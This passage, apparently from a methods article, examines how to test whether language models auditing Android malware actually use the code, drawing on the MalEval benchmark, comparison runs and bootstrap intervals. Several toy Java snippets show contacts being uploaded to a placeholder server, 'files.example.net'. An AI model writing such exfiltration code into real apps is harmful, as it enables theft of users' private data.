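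Retraining is often impractical anyway. *Improving Feature Attribution through Input-specific Network Pruning* (2019) tested eight methods at five removal levels, with three training runs each. That makes 120 runs, too many for ImageNet, so it used CIFAR-10, a much smaller dataset. With a commercial language model, the tester usually has neither the weights nor the training data. Some providers offer fine-tuning, but a fine-tuned model is no longer the one that analysts use, and MalEval's 62 expert reports would be a very small training set.

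The remaining step is to make the reduced input as ordinary as possible. Hase and colleagues compared five ways of removing tokens from the input to models without special training. Using a mask token, or hiding the removed tokens from the model's attention, did the least damage. Deleting tokens, which shortens the text, was up to 4.7 points worse. Filling the gaps with plausible words from another language model, and combining the predictions over many fillings, was often more than 10 points worse than the best method. Refills therefore need care, because plausible words have meanings of their own and may point to a different answer.

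Even so, the objection is probably weaker against MalEval's test than against tests that grey out pixels or mask words, because the reduced input is still a list of real function summaries from one app, in the usual format. The objection is stronger when a tester deletes lines from inside a function, because the remaining code may not compile.

### Choices when refilling

The tester first has to decide whether to match the number of items or the number of tokens. MalEval swaps equal numbers of items, which works reasonably well for summaries. If an input holds 300 summaries, MalEval's averages imply about 62 tokens each, so 30 swaps can't change the total much. Decompiled code has about 610 tokens per item on the same assumption. If the tester removes eight functions of 900 tokens each and adds eight of 150, the input shrinks by 6,000 tokens, more than a tenth of MalEval's average for decompiled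 code. For code, it is better to match tokens by replacing each removed function with a lower-ranked one of similar length. Padding with comments is a poor substitute, as the SerenityOS parser showed.

Refilling can also change the order of the input. MalEval lists summaries by rank, so if the reduced input follows the same rule, the item in place 31 moves to the top and the refill goes to the end. Stoltman and colleagues cite earlier findings that language models do worse when the relevant information is in the middle of a long prompt, so moving the remaining evidence could change the score. The Maikspy example keeps that evidence in place by putting the refill in the empty places, but then the least relevant items come first. The cleanest solution is to shuffle the full input once, keep that order, and put each new item in the place of the one it replaces.

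In MalEval, an item consists of a function's signature, its description and its sensitivity score. If the prompt includes the scores, the reduced input has lower numbers, and the model might report less for that reason alone. The tester can avoid this by leaving the scores out of both inputs.

Item 3 in the Maikspy example shows the problem with calls to removed functions. The tester can rewrite that summary without access to the removed function, which might produce "Opens the first screen and sets a timer". Removing `Main.onCreate` as well would be simpler, but it takes out more than the ranking required. In raw code, the call can stay, since real code often calls library functions that the reader can't see. But a name such as `uploadContacts` reveals what the removed function did, so the tester should use a neutral name in both inputs.

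The refill can come from the same app or from another one. Code from the same app fits in better but may contain more of the malicious behaviour. Code from a harmless app avoids that problem, but its package names and libraries won't match, and it will stand out if the malware's author has scrambled the names in the code, as in 62 of MalEval's 230 malware samples. A model may also make false claims about harmless code, as happened with WorkManager. Code from the same app is the better default, provided that someone checks it against the expert report.

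Small apps may not have enough functions to refill the input. To remove 30 items from an input of 300 and replace them all, an app needs at least 330 functions. MalEval's average is well above that, but its smallest apps may still fall short. When an app does, the tester can make the full input smaller. For an app with N functions and a removal share s, the full input can hold at most N / (1 + s) items. With 200 functions and a 10% share, that is 181 items, of which the tester removes 18 and replaces them with 18 of the 19 left over. Larger shares require more spare functions, so at 80% the same app supports a full input of only 111 items. If an input that small would leave out decisive code, it is better to exclude the app and report how many apps were excluded for this reason.

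## Scoring the drop against comparison runs

A drop of 25 points between the full and reduced inputs is hard to interpret by itself. Part of it may come from swapping the items, and the largest possible drop depends on how many points the model scores without any code. The tester therefore needs a suitable score, comparison runs and an uncertainty interval.

### What to score

MalEval scores evidence claims, each a triple of an action, an asset and a target, such as (STEAL, CONTACTS, C2_SERVER). A C2 server is the machine an attacker uses to control the malware. Zheng and colleagues compare a claim with one in the expert report and add 0.6 for a matching action, 0.3 for a matching asset and 0.1 for a matching target. They count the claim as correct if the total is at least 0.8.

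A claim with the wrong target therefore scores 0.9 and passes, while one with the wrong asset scores 0.7 and fails. If the tester removes Maikspy's upload function but leaves the function that reads contacts, a model that still reports stolen contacts without naming a destination gets full credit, and evidence F1 doesn't change.

The yes-or-no verdict is even less sensitive. When Zheng and colleagues took caller and callee information out of the summaries, Claude 3.7 Sonnet's evidence F1 fell from 29.95% to 22.45%, while the share of malware it called malicious rose slightly, from 89.69% to 91.20%. They removed context rather than the top-ranked functions, but the verdict can also stay the same in sensitivity ablation when an app has several incriminating functions.

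A model's verdicts may also stay the same because it calls most code vulnerable. Liu and Gao (2026), in *Trusting the Tool*, gave models C and C++ functions with notes from a program-analysis tool, some of which were deliberately false. One model, qwen-plus, found 88% of the vulnerable functions with true notes and 87% with notes that falsely said the missing check was there. It also flagged most of the repaired functions, so its steady recall is poor evidence that it recognised the notes as false. Liu and Gao therefore measure how far verdicts move towards the answer that the changed evidence favours. For removal, the equivalent would be the share of "safe" verdicts with the top items removed, minus the share with random items removed. This helps, but a model that always answers "vulnerable" would still score zero.

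The threat category can change even when the verdict does not. If a banking trojan loses the code for its fake login screens, "spyware" may become a reasonable label. However, models often get the category wrong before any code is removed. Claude 3.7 Sonnet and Gemini-2.5-Pro misclassified every rootkit sample in MalEval, so removing code could not have lowered their category scores on those apps.

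The probability of an answer is the finest measure, because it can fall from 0.99 to 0.60 without changing the verdict. *ERASER* (2019), a benchmark for explanations of language-model predictions, uses this drop under the name comprehensiveness:

drop = p(original answer | full input) − p(original answer | reduced input)

*Navigating Disagreement Among Criteria for Evaluating Explanation Faithfulness* (2026) makes explicit that the drop must compare the probability of the same answer on the full and reduced inputs. If a model gives "spyware" a probability of 0.90 on the full input and "adware" 0.90 on the reduced one, comparing the two top probabilities shows no drop, even though the probability of "spyware" may have fallen to 0.05. Measuring the drop in one answer's probability requires no expert report, but it doesn't show whether the original answer was right, and many commercial models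 don't reveal the probability.

For malware auditing, evidence F1 is the best main score, with the verdict reported beside it. Probability suits a detector that reads one function and answers without writing out its reasoning.

### The expert report stays the same

MalEval scores both runs against the same expert report, which still lists the operations whose code the tester has removed. A model that correctly reports only what is in the remaining code therefore loses points.

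Suppose the original report lists five operations and the tester removes the code for two of them. One model reports the three that remain, while another recognises the malware family and still reports all five. The table shows both models' scores against the original report, then against a shortened report without the two removed operations.

| Model's claims on the reduced input | F1, original report | F1, shortened report |
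|---|---|---|
| The three remaining operations | 0.75 | 1.00 |
| All five operations | 1.00 | 0.75 |

The original report is the right reference for ΔS because the test is meant to show whether claims disappear along with their code. The shortened report is the better reference for judging how well the model audited the reduced app, since a lower score against the original does not mean the audit was bad. But to produce the shortened report, someone has to trace every operation to its code.

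The reports may also list behaviour that a particular sample lacks, because security companies often write them about a whole malware family. In MalEval, 62 reports cover all 230 malicious apps. Some of the listed behaviour may also be in native code, which MalEval's analysis does not read. A model that earns points for either kind of behaviour will keep them whatever is removed.

Sometimes removing code changes the correct answer. If all the malicious code is gone, the reduced app is harmless, so "malicious" is now wrong even though it still counts as right under the original label. Similarly, deleting the final write makes the small C program with the 69-slot array safe, while deleting the check on `NumberOfPipes` makes the FreeRDP function vulnerable.

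The tester should decide the right answer for each reduced input before running the model. Where the right answer has changed, the useful figure is how often the model switches to the new answer. Measuring accuracy against the old label would reward a model for ignoring the change. If nobody can tell whether enough malicious code remains, it is better to leave the app out of the verdict score and keep it in the evidence score.

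### Three comparison runs

ΔS uses only two runs. Three more make it much easier to interpret.

**Random removal.** The tester removes the same number of items, chosen at random, and refills the input. *Evaluating the Faithfulness of Importance Measures in NLP* (Madsen, Meade and colleagues, 2021) bases its test on this comparison. If a ranking is accurate, removing the top items should reduce performance more than removing random ones. *ERASER* also reports results for randomly scored words as a baseline.

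The comparison run should use the same refill as the main run, so that any harm from the refill appears in both scores. One random draw isn't enough, because the score depends partly on luck. With five decisive functions among 300, a random set of 30 contains at least one of them about 41% of the time. Averaging five or ten draws per app would give a steadier score.

**Removal of the lowest-ranked items.** In an input of 300 items, the tester replaces those ranked 271 to 300 with those ranked 301 to 330. The two groups have nearly the same rank, so the score should barely change. If it falls by several points, either swapping items is itself harmful or decisive code was ranked near the bottom of the input. A rise suggests that decisive code was ranked just below the cut.

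In the no-code run, the model gets the usual instructions but no function summaries, and writes a report. The report's score estimates how well the model can do from its prior alone. In *Evaluating and Characterizing Human Rationales*, Carton, Rathore and Tan (2020) call the difference between a model's results on the full input and on an empty one the "null difference". Madsen and colleagues use the score on fully masked text as a lower bound, because their datasets are often biased and a model can beat chance without reading the text.

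The same could easily happen in a malware audit. MalEval limits claims to 16 actions, 20 assets and 13 targets, so a model that guesses the usual spyware combinations will sometimes be right. If the full input includes the package name, the no-code input should include it too. Otherwise, points the model gets by using the name will look as if they came from the code.

Some models will decline to write a report when they are given no code. A refusal scores zero, but it doesn't show that the model has no prior. The tester can ask for a best guess, as long as every run uses the same instruction.

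### A worked example

Take an invented model with these average evidence F1 scores, on a scale from 0 to 100:

| Run | Evidence F1 |
|---|---|
| Full input | 60 |
| Random items removed | 55 |
| Top-ranked items removed | 35 |
| No code | 30 |

The calculation takes four lines:

- raw drop (ΔS) = 60 − 35 = 25
- drop beyond random removal = 55 − 35 = 20
- points the code contributes = 60 − 30 = 30
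- share = 20 / 30 ≈ 0.67

The model scores 30 of its 60 points without seeing any code, so removing code should not lower its score by more than about 30. Removing the top-ranked functions lowers the score by 20 points more than removing random ones, which is two thirds of what the code contributes. Someone who divided the raw drop by the full score would get 42% and might conclude that the model made only moderate use of the removed functions.

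Subtracting the random drop assumes that all five of its points come from the swapping itself. Some probably arise because the random draws happened to hit decisive code, so two thirds is likely a slight underestimate.

Other ways of dividing the drop give different results. Carton and colleagues divide the raw drop by the null difference, which here gives 25/30, or 0.83. Madsen and colleagues measure both differences from the random-removal score. They remove increasing shares of the text and divide the area between the random and top-removed curves by the area between the random curve and the fully masked score. At a single share, that would be (55 − 35) / (55 − 30) = 0.80. None of these methods is wrong, but readers can't compare figures from different studies without knowing which one each study used, so it is best to publish all four scores.

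The share can also exceed 1, because the score with the top items removed may fall below the no-code score if the refill leads the model to make false claims. *Faithfulness Measurable Masked Language Models* (2023) limits Madsen and colleagues' normalisation to absolute importance measures, which rank items by the size of their effect, regardless of direction. Masking the most helpful items first could push a model's score below the one it gets with everything masked.

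### Weak models and the choice of divisor

F1 cannot go below zero, so ΔS cannot be larger than the score on the full input. Llama-3.1-8B, for instance, had an evidence F1 of 6.94% in MalEval, so its score could not have dropped by 10 points even if it had depended entirely on the removed functions. A small absolute drop from a weak model is therefore poor evidence that it ignores the code.

Dividing the drop by the full score puts weak and strong models on the same scale, but it also magnifies noise when the full score is low. For a model that scores 7, losing two points is a 29% drop, and a few claims that happen not to match could cause it. Dividing also doesn't account for the prior. The model in the worked example could rely on the top-ranked functions for everything it learns from the code and still lose only half its score, because the rest comes from the prior.

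Dividing the drop by the points that the code contributes corrects for the prior. Carton and colleagues did the equivalent with FEVER, a dataset of claims that Wikipedia passages support or refute. They removed the passages that people had marked as evidence and measured the fall in the model's probability. The fall was larger for "refutes" than for "supports", but the two were similar after division by the null difference, so the researchers attribute the gap to the model's bias towards one answer. On two other datasets, covering film reviews and reading comprehension, a gap between the classes remained after the division.

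This divisor fails when the code contributes almost nothing. Suppose a model scores 31 on the full input, 30.5 after random removal, 29.5 after top removal and 30 with no code. Its share is (30.5 − 29.5)/(31 − 30), or 100%, although it hardly uses the code. The tester should calculate the share from scores averaged over all apps, because the divisor will be near zero for many individual apps.

Neither divisor corrects for how a model combines its evidence. *Normalized AOPC* (Edin, Motzfeldt and colleagues, 2024) shows this with four tiny models that take four yes-or-no features, a to d. Each model outputs 1 when all the features are present and 0 when none are.

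| Model | Output | Drop after removing the best first feature | Average drop over four removals |
|---|---|---|---|
| P | 0.2a + 0.3b + 0.1c + 0.4d | 0.40 | 0.75 |
| Q | 0.1b + 0.7c + 0.2d | 0.70 | 0.90 |
| R | 0.7(a or b) + 0.3(c or d) | 0.00 | 0.60 |
| S | 0.7(a and b) + 0.3(c and d) | 0.70 | 0.925 |

The last column assumes that features are removed in the most damaging order. For P, the drops after one, two, three and four removals are 0.4, 0.7, 0.9 and 1.0. Their average, 0.75, is the AOPC (area over the perturbation curve) in the title. All four models depend entirely on their input, yet their averages range from 0.60 to 0.925. P spreads its reliance over more features than Q, and R can lose either feature of a pair without effect.

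Edin and colleagues correct for this by finding the lowest and highest averages that any order of removal can produce for a given model and input:

normalised score = (average drop − lowest) / (highest − lowest)

With the most damaging order, every model in the table scores 1. The limits also differ between real models. On short Yelp reviews, the highest possible average drop was around 0.3 for one classifier and 0.8 for another, so a drop of 0.25 would be high only for the first. Normalising changed which models looked best, but it mostly preserved the order of the ranking methods within each model. Edin and colleagues conclude that normalising is necessary for comparing models, but generally not for comparing ranking methods on one model.

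The method takes too long to use on malware reports. Even its faster search needs about B × N² runs for N items, where B is the number of candidate orders it keeps at each step. With 300 summaries and B = 5, that is 450,000 reports per app, which would take DeepSeek-R1 more than a year. The experiments used small classifiers such as BERT, which can handle a hundred features in about a minute.

The share from the four runs is a substitute that takes less work but corrects for less. It accounts for the prior and the swap, but P would still look less dependent than Q if the tester removed one feature. Removing several shares in turn, as in the earlier comparison of models A and B, at least shows whether a model spreads its reliance widely.

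### Putting an interval on the drop

A drop of 20 points on 230 apps would not be exactly 20 on another 230. It would also change somewhat if the same model wrote the reports again. The interval should cover both kinds of variation.

Both runs use the same apps, so the tester starts by calculating the drop for each app. This pairing cancels much of the variation in difficulty between apps. Suppose scores vary between apps with a standard deviation of 25 points in each run, and the two runs have a correlation of 0.8. With 230 apps, the standard error of the average drop is about 1.0 point if the scores are paired, compared with about 2.3 points if the runs are treated as unrelated samples. *Adding Error Bars to Evals* (Miller, 2024) recommends pairing whenever two sets of scores come from the same questions.

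However, the apps are not independent. MalEval's 230 malicious apps belong to 56 families, and its 32 rootkits belong to four families. Samples from one family often share code and an expert report, so a mistake in that report affects every sample that shares it.

In an invented set of ten apps, six belong to one family and each show a drop of 40 points. The other four come from different families and show drops of 0, 5, 0 and 10. The average drop is 25.5 points. Treating the apps as ten independent results gives a standard error of about 6 points, while grouping them by family gives about 10. On DROP, a reading test with many questions about each passage, Miller found that the grouped standard error was about three times the ordinary one.

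A bootstrap handles pairing and grouping together. It estimates uncertainty by drawing new samples from the existing data:

1. Average the repeated reports for each app, separately for each run.
2. Draw 56 families at random, with replacement, so that some appear twice and others not at all.
3. Take every app in the drawn families, with its scores from all four runs.
4. Recalculate the four average scores, the drop beyond random removal and the share.
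5. Repeat steps 2 to 4 about 2,000 times. The middle 95% of the results is the interval.

*evalci* (2026), a Python library for comparing model evaluations, has a function that resamples whole groups in this way. To compare two models, the tester should use the same resampled families for both. For verdicts, Liu and Gao use McNemar's test, which considers only the cases that one run got right and the other got wrong. In one of their comparisons, the model judged ten functions correctly only with true notes and one only with false notes, which gives p = 0.012.

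Averaging repeated reports reduces the noise in the model's output. In Miller's example, where answers are right or wrong and question difficulty is evenly spread, two answers per question cut the variance by a third and four cut it by half. The reduction can't exceed two thirds, because the remaining variation comes from the questions. Wang (2025), in *Measuring all the noises of LLM Evals*, found that output noise usually exceeded question noise in paired comparisons between models. On HumanEval, a set of 164 programming problems, pairing lowered the smallest detectable difference from 11 points to 8, and adding averaging over repeated answers lowered it to between 2 and 4. Those figures come from tests of correctness, so the gain for evidence F1 could be different.

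Setting the temperature to 0, which makes the model choose its most probable next token, is not a substitute for repetition. MalEval uses this setting, which makes reports more repeatable. But Miller warns that it can change the average score or turn output noise into larger differences between questions, which repetition can't reduce. Generating four reports for each of the four runs would take about 23 minutes per app at DeepSeek-R1's speed, not counting any extra random draws.

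A simple check on the procedure is to run the full input twice and calculate the "drop" between the two sets of reports. The true drop is zero, so the interval should usually include zero. *A Calibrated Instrument for Detecting Disposition Drift in Language Models* (2026) includes a null test of this kind on two samples from the same model. It also cites a finding by Solomon Messing that the standard errors in typical language-model evaluations are 40 to 60% too small.

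The share needs more caution than the drop because its divisor is also uncertain. If the interval for the number of points the code contributes includes zero, the tester should report the four scores without the share.

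## What a large or a small drop establishes

Zheng and colleagues read a large drop as a sign that a model's reasoning "depends on high-value code evidence rather than prior-driven shortcuts". A drop well beyond the random-removal run is good evidence that the removed functions affected the score. Whether those functions were "high-value" depends on the ranking, which in MalEval comes from the tested model itself. No drop, however large, establishes that the model reasoned from the code rather than relying on shortcuts from its priors.

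A large drop is compatible with a strong prior. The model in the four-run example scored 30 of its 60 points with no code, yet removing its top-ranked functions lowered its score by 20 points more than removing random ones.

Memorised information can even cause a large drop. Suppose Maikspy's upload function contains the address `files.example.net`, and a model was trained on a published report that links this server to Maikspy. The model identifies the family from the address and repeats the published findings, including operations it did not find in the code. If the tester removes the upload function, the model no longer identifies the family and all of those claims disappear, although most of them came from memory. The no-code run does not reveal this either, because an empty input contains nothing that identifies the family.

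### Three readers

Take an invented spyware app whose expert report lists five malicious operations. Three readers audit it:

- The constant reader always answers "malicious" and attaches the same five stock claims, three of which happen to match the report.
- The name matcher looks for API names, the names of the functions that Android and its libraries offer to apps. If it sees one call that reads contacts and another that uploads something, it reports stolen contacts.
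- The data follower traces data from source to sink, meaning from where private data enters the program to where it leaves. It reports stolen contacts only if the contacts reach the upload.

The name matcher and the data follower each report four of the five operations and nothing else, so each has an evidence F1 of 2 × 4 / (4 + 5) ≈ 0.89. The tester then removes the top-ranked functions, which contain all the code behind those four operations, and replaces them with harmless functions. The random-removal run happens to leave the decisive code in place.

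| Reader | Full input | Random items removed | Top-ranked items removed | Verdict after top removal |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Constant reader | 0.60 | 0.60 | 0.60 | malicious |
| Name matcher | 0.89 | 0.89 | 0.00 | harmless |
| Data follower | 0.89 | 0.89 | 0.00 | harmless |

The test exposes the constant reader but can't tell the other two apart. The removed functions contained both the API names and the data flow, so each reader lost what it was using. A better ranking or a larger share wouldn't help, since the shortcut lies inside the decisive code. The two readers would disagree about a harmless app like this one:

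```java
List<Contact> people = readContacts(ctx);
showOnScreen(people);
ftp.upload("files.example.net", crashLog);
```

The name matcher reports stolen contacts because both calls are in the code. The data follower doesn't, because the code only displays `people` on the screen. To tell them apart, the tester has to change the evidence instead of removing it, for example by using a patched version or new names.

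Some MalEval results suggest that models were matching names. They were fairly reliable on behaviours that show up in recognisable Android APIs, such as stealing private data or displaying ads, but tended to miss stealthy downloads and premium-service fraud, which have no stable API signature. However, the missed behaviours often depend on encrypted strings or what happens while the app runs, so even a careful reader would find them harder to spot in static code.

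A model can cite relevant code without using it correctly. Zheng and colleagues asked three other language models to judge whether the functions cited for each claim supported it. Gemini-2.5-Pro scored 92.08%, but its evidence F1 was only 24.24%. It usually pointed to relevant functions but missed many of the operations in the expert reports or described them differently. The researchers also read 350 reports by hand. Of the failures in those reports, 23.56% came from models that had found relevant pieces of an attack but failed to connect them. Removing those pieces could lower a model's score even if it never understood the attack.

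*Do Fine-Tuned LLMs Understand Vulnerabilities?* (2026) tested five models fine-tuned to detect vulnerabilities on pairs of vulnerable and patched code. Their results varied with how similar the two versions looked on the surface, but the correlation was below 0.1 in absolute value for every model, so surface similarity explains very little by itself. Models that wrote out their reasoning still misread control flow and the behaviour of API functions.

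### Duplicated evidence

A small drop is just as hard to interpret, because a model that depends entirely on the code can produce one. The simplest reason is that the program does the same thing in two places:

```java
// Alarm.onReceive, ranked 1st: removed
ftp.upload("files.example.net", writeToFile(readContacts(ctx)));

// Sync.onConnected, ranked 41st: still in the input
http.post("https://files.example.net/c", toJson(readContacts(ctx)));
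```

After the tester removes the top 30 functions, a model can still correctly report that contacts go to a remote server if the remaining code shows this. ΔS is then close to zero, even though the model based its claim on code in both runs. Summaries of neighbouring functions can also repeat the same evidence.

Yuan, Yao and colleagues (2026), in *One Fact, Many Places*, measured this effect in long documents, where the same figure often appears in both a chart and a sentence. They gave four models six-page inputs with at least two copies of a fact, then covered either the copy that the benchmark marks as evidence or every copy they had found. Covering only the marked copy left 76% to 94% of the correct answers intact, while covering all the copies they had found left 20% to 53%.

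For 41% to 56% of the correct answers, depending on the model, covering the marked copy left the answer unchanged, but covering every copy made it wrong. A tester who covered only one place would have missed this dependence. Covering random lines of the same area changed at most about 10% of the answers. The samples were small, with 25 to 32 correct answers per model, and the study used documents instead of code, so the exact percentages don't carry over to malware.

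Yuan and colleagues also point out that neither kind of masking shows which of two redundant pieces of code the model relied on. If functions A and B both send contacts, removing A, B or both can't show whether the model relied on A when it had the full input. This usually doesn't matter for sensitivity ablation, since either function would justify the claim.

The remedy is to find the copies and remove them together. Yuan and colleagues automated this by having a model write down the fact, search the document for possible copies and check each one. This achieved 78% of the extra effect of covering every annotated copy. A cruder rule, which covered every block of text containing a matching string, removed the answers at least as well but covered three times the area, and only about 27% of the additional blocks were real copies. In code, a search for `readContacts` would find both functions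 above, but also every harmless screen that lists contacts, so someone should check the matches before removing them.

Ranking functions by influence can make the problem worse. When Yuan and colleagues ran ContextCite on inputs with copies, the marked block scored about a third of what such blocks scored in inputs without copies. *Context Dependence and Reliability in Autoregressive Language Models* (2026) deliberately credits each piece of the input only with what the rest can't supply. That makes sense for finding unique evidence, but a tester who used it to choose what to remove would probably leave both upload functions in place.

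### A poor ranking or a low starting score

A poor ranking can leave the decisive functions in the input, as happened with model B. Removing a larger share of the code or using an outside ranking can reveal this.

A low starting score also limits the drop, and the MalEval results show how much this affects comparisons. The last column divides ΔS by the evidence F1 on the full input.

| Model | Evidence F1 (%) | ΔS (points) | Share of score lost |
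|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 29.95 | 12.34 | 41% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 26.60 | 10.45 | 39% |
| Gemini-2.5-Pro | 24.24 | 11.21 | 46% |
| Qwen3-32B | 19.82 | 8.57 | 43% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 19.12 | 5.89 | 31% |
| Qwen2.5-Coder-14B | 12.40 | 6.87 | 55% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 6.94 | 1.41 | 20% |

Claude 3.7 Sonnet has the largest ΔS, but Qwen2.5-Coder-14B lost the largest share of its score. Most of the spread in ΔS among the stronger models reflects differences in their original scores.

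Zheng and colleagues take Llama-3.1-8B's drop of 1.41 points to suggest that it relies on priors instead of reasoning about the code. Its low baseline can't fully explain the small drop, since Llama also lost the smallest share of its score. But a model that understands little of the code and has no useful prior either would produce the same baseline and drop. Running Llama without any code would help separate these two explanations. If it scored about 5, the prior would be a good explanation for its result. If it scored close to zero, its few points must have come from the input, and the ranking would be the next thing to check.

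### Recovering the answer from what remains

A model can sometimes work out the answer even when no copy of the evidence is left. Suppose the tester removes both upload functions, but the refill contains this line:

```java
new File(dir, "contacts_sent.csv").delete();
```

The line only deletes a file, but the file's name still suggests that contacts left the phone, and an analyst might well draw the same conclusion. The small drop would then come from either good inference or reading too much into a file name, and the score can't show which.

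When Zheng and colleagues added metadata to the input, Gemini-2.5-Pro's evidence F1 rose by about two points, but its ΔS fell from 11.21 to 6.22 points. They suggest that metadata may overshadow the model's understanding of individual functions. Alternatively, Gemini may have read the functions just as closely and used the metadata to fill in what was missing from the reduced input.

The model can still draw on its memory, whatever the tester removes. Abbas, Zia and Windridge (2026), in *Cited but Unused*, tested how often models do this while appearing to use their sources. They gave questions and retrieved passages to six open models with 0.5 to 14 billion parameters. Then they replaced a value in the passages, such as a year, with a false one and asked again. A model that repeated the original value was answering from memory. This happened for 1.2% to 15.7% of the claims they could test,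 depending on the model.

The models were also asked for the same values without any passages. Qwen2.5-7B could supply the original value for 220 claims, but it followed the altered passage for 191 of these when given one.

The no-code run shows how much a model can score without the code, but not where its claims came from when the code was present. A model that scores 60 with the code and 30 without it may have taken all 60 points from the code, or only 30. The difference between the two scores measures what the code adds, which may be less than how much of the score came from the code.

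Deleting passages was a poor way to tell whether a claim came from a passage or from memory. Abbas and colleagues removed passages one at a time and used the fall in the claim's probability to guess its source. Across the six models, the AUROC was 0.541 to 0.667. AUROC is the chance that a method ranks a random positive case above a random negative one, so 0.5 is guessing. Their explanation is that a model can often produce the same value from another passage or from memory, so the fall is small whichever source it used.

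### Whether the removed evidence is enough by itself

*ERASER* pairs comprehensiveness, the drop in probability after removal, with a measure called sufficiency. Sufficiency reverses the operation by keeping the chosen evidence and removing everything else:

sufficiency = p(answer | full input) − p(answer | evidence alone)

Confusingly, a low sufficiency score means that the evidence is sufficient. Suppose a model gives "spyware" a probability of 0.90 on the full input, 0.30 without the upload functions and 0.85 with only the upload functions. Comprehensiveness is 0.90 − 0.30 = 0.60, so the functions mattered to the answer. Sufficiency is 0.90 − 0.85 = 0.05, so they were nearly enough to produce it on their own.

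That example is the first row below. The other rows, also invented, show why the two measures are more useful together.

| Situation | Full input | Evidence removed | Evidence alone | Comprehensiveness | Sufficiency |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| All the evidence is in the chosen functions | 0.90 | 0.30 | 0.85 | 0.60 | 0.05 |
| The answer also needs other code | 0.90 | 0.30 | 0.40 | 0.60 | 0.50 |
| The evidence has a copy elsewhere | 0.90 | 0.88 | 0.85 | 0.02 | 0.05 |
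| The model always answers "spyware" | 0.90 | 0.90 | 0.90 | 0.00 | 0.00 |

A removal test alone gives the same result for the top two rows. A sufficiency test separates those two but not the bottom two. To tell the bottom two apart, the tester needs the no-code run, where the model that always answers "spyware" stays at 0.90 and the other should fall.

In real models, too, evidence can matter a lot without being enough on its own. *ERASER* averages both measures over several cuts, from the top 1% to the top 50% of the words, and compares each ranking with a random one. The figures below are for LIME, a method that estimates each word's influence by fitting a simple model to many altered inputs.

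| Dataset | Comprehensiveness, LIME | Comprehensiveness, random | Sufficiency, LIME | Sufficiency, random |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Film reviews | 0.187 | 0.058 | 0.093 | 0.330 |
| e-SNLI | 0.437 | 0.081 | 0.389 | 0.487 |

The e-SNLI task is to decide whether one sentence follows from another. Removing the top-ranked words had a large effect on this task, but keeping only those words worked little better than keeping random ones. The texts average 16 tokens, so the smaller selections contain only a word or two, which is rarely enough to compare two sentences. Keeping only the top-ranked words worked much better on film reviews.

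In a malware audit, the tester would keep the 30 top-ranked summaries, replace the other 270 with harmless functions, and score evidence F1 as usual. This replaces many more summaries than the ordinary test does, so the input is more likely to look unnatural. *ERASER* (DeYoung et al.) presents both measures as a starting point and describes how best to measure a model's reliance on evidence as an open question.

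### Scoring both classes

When a model's verdict changes from "vulnerable" to "safe" after a removal, it may have lost the evidence, or it may answer "safe" whenever something disturbs it. A study of a model's internal parts shows how lopsided the effect of a disturbance can be. Al Atiiq, Zhou and Gehrmann (2026), in *Dissecting the Black Box*, examined Gemma-2-2b, a 2-billion-parameter Google model, on C and C++ functions from PrimeVul. They left the code alone and disabled parts of the model:

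1. They kept only functions that the model had classified correctly, so accuracy started at 100% for both classes.
2. They replaced the activity of one layer with its average over the dataset, so that the layer no longer carried information about the function at hand.
3. In separate runs, they switched off a single attention head, or the 20 neurons in layer 7 whose activity rose most on vulnerable code compared with safe code.
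4. They classified the functions again.

| Part disabled | Vulnerable code correct | Safe code correct | All code correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| Layer 6 | 27.7% | 94.6% | 76.4% |
| Layer 7 | 19.3% | 63.1% | 51.2% |
| Layer 10 | 19.3% | 96.9% | 75.7% |
| Layer 11 | 6.0% | 64.9% | 48.9% |
| 20 neurons in layer 7 | 50.6% | 94.1% | 82.3% |
| One attention head in layer 0 | 61.5% | 95.1% | 85.9% |

Without layer 6 or layer 10, the model missed most of the vulnerable code but still gave the right verdict on nearly all the safe code. Layers 7 and 11 fit this pattern less well, because disabling either one also made the model lose more than a third of its correct "safe" verdicts.

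The overall accuracy greatly understates the damage. The averages imply that only about 27% of the tested functions were vulnerable, so without layer 10 the model was still right three quarters of the time, even though it missed four out of five vulnerable functions. Its score of 96.9% on safe code doesn't show that it could still recognise safe code, since a program that always prints "safe" would score 100%.

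Al Atiiq and colleagues explain the model's behaviour with "safety detectors", attention heads that respond to safe patterns such as bounds checks. On their account, the model answers "vulnerable" when these heads don't activate. But the head they disabled in layer 0 is one of their five strongest safety detectors, so disabling it should have made the model flag more code. Instead, the model missed 38.5% of the vulnerable functions it had previously caught. The experiments are better evidence that this one small model tends to answer "safe" when part of it is damaged.

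Removing input could expose the same kind of default. A model that defaults to "safe" may show a large drop on vulnerable code because the refill made the code harder to interpret. A model that defaults to "malicious" can give the same malware verdicts even after all its evidence is removed.

MalEval has a small example of the second problem. When Zheng and colleagues removed caller and callee information, Claude 3.7 Sonnet's verdicts on malware barely changed, but the share of harmless apps it cleared fell from 88% to 76%. That is a difference of only three of the 25 harmless apps, so it's weak evidence, but they would have missed it if they had scored only the malware.

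The tester should run every comparison on both malicious and harmless apps and report the two rates separately. If the random-removal run makes the model answer "safe" more often in both groups, the swap itself explains part of any drop in malware detection. In harmless apps, the top-ranked functions are usually the ones that look most suspicious, so removing them should make the model more likely to call the apps safe. If it calls fewer harmless apps safe, the refill may be prompting false claims.

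### From result to next test

| Result | Permitted conclusion | Next test |
|---|---|---|
| Top removal costs much more than random removal | The removed items affected the score | Change what the evidence does but keep its names, then the reverse |
| Top and random removal cost about the same | The top-ranked items had no special effect | Remove the lowest-ranked items, then try larger shares |
| Small drop, and the no-code score is close to the full score | The model can earn most of its score without the code | Change a fact in the code and see whether the claim follows |
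| Small drop, and the no-code score is far below the full score | The model uses something that is still in the input | Remove all copies together, or use an outside ranking |
| Small drop from a low full score | Very little | Add a no-code run and test apps on which the model does better |
| High comprehensiveness and a high sufficiency value | The removed items mattered but were not enough alone | Return other items in groups until the answer recovers |
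| Malware verdicts hold, but the model clears fewer harmless apps | The change pushed the model towards "malicious" | Run random removal on both classes |
| The score rises | The removed items misled the model, or the refill helped it | Read the refill and compare the claims in the two reports |

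## Follow-up tests that change the evidence or withhold all of it

Removing the top-ranked functions could not distinguish the name matcher from the data follower. A tester can tell them apart by keeping the code and changing either its names or what it sends. The twin below keeps the suggestive names but sends something harmless, while the renamed version behaves exactly like the original.

```java
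// Original: the contacts leave the phone
List<Contact> people = readContacts(ctx);
ftp.upload("files.example.net", writeToFile(people));

// Patched twin: the contacts stay on the phone
List<Contact> people = readContacts(ctx);
ftp.upload("files.example.net", crashLog);

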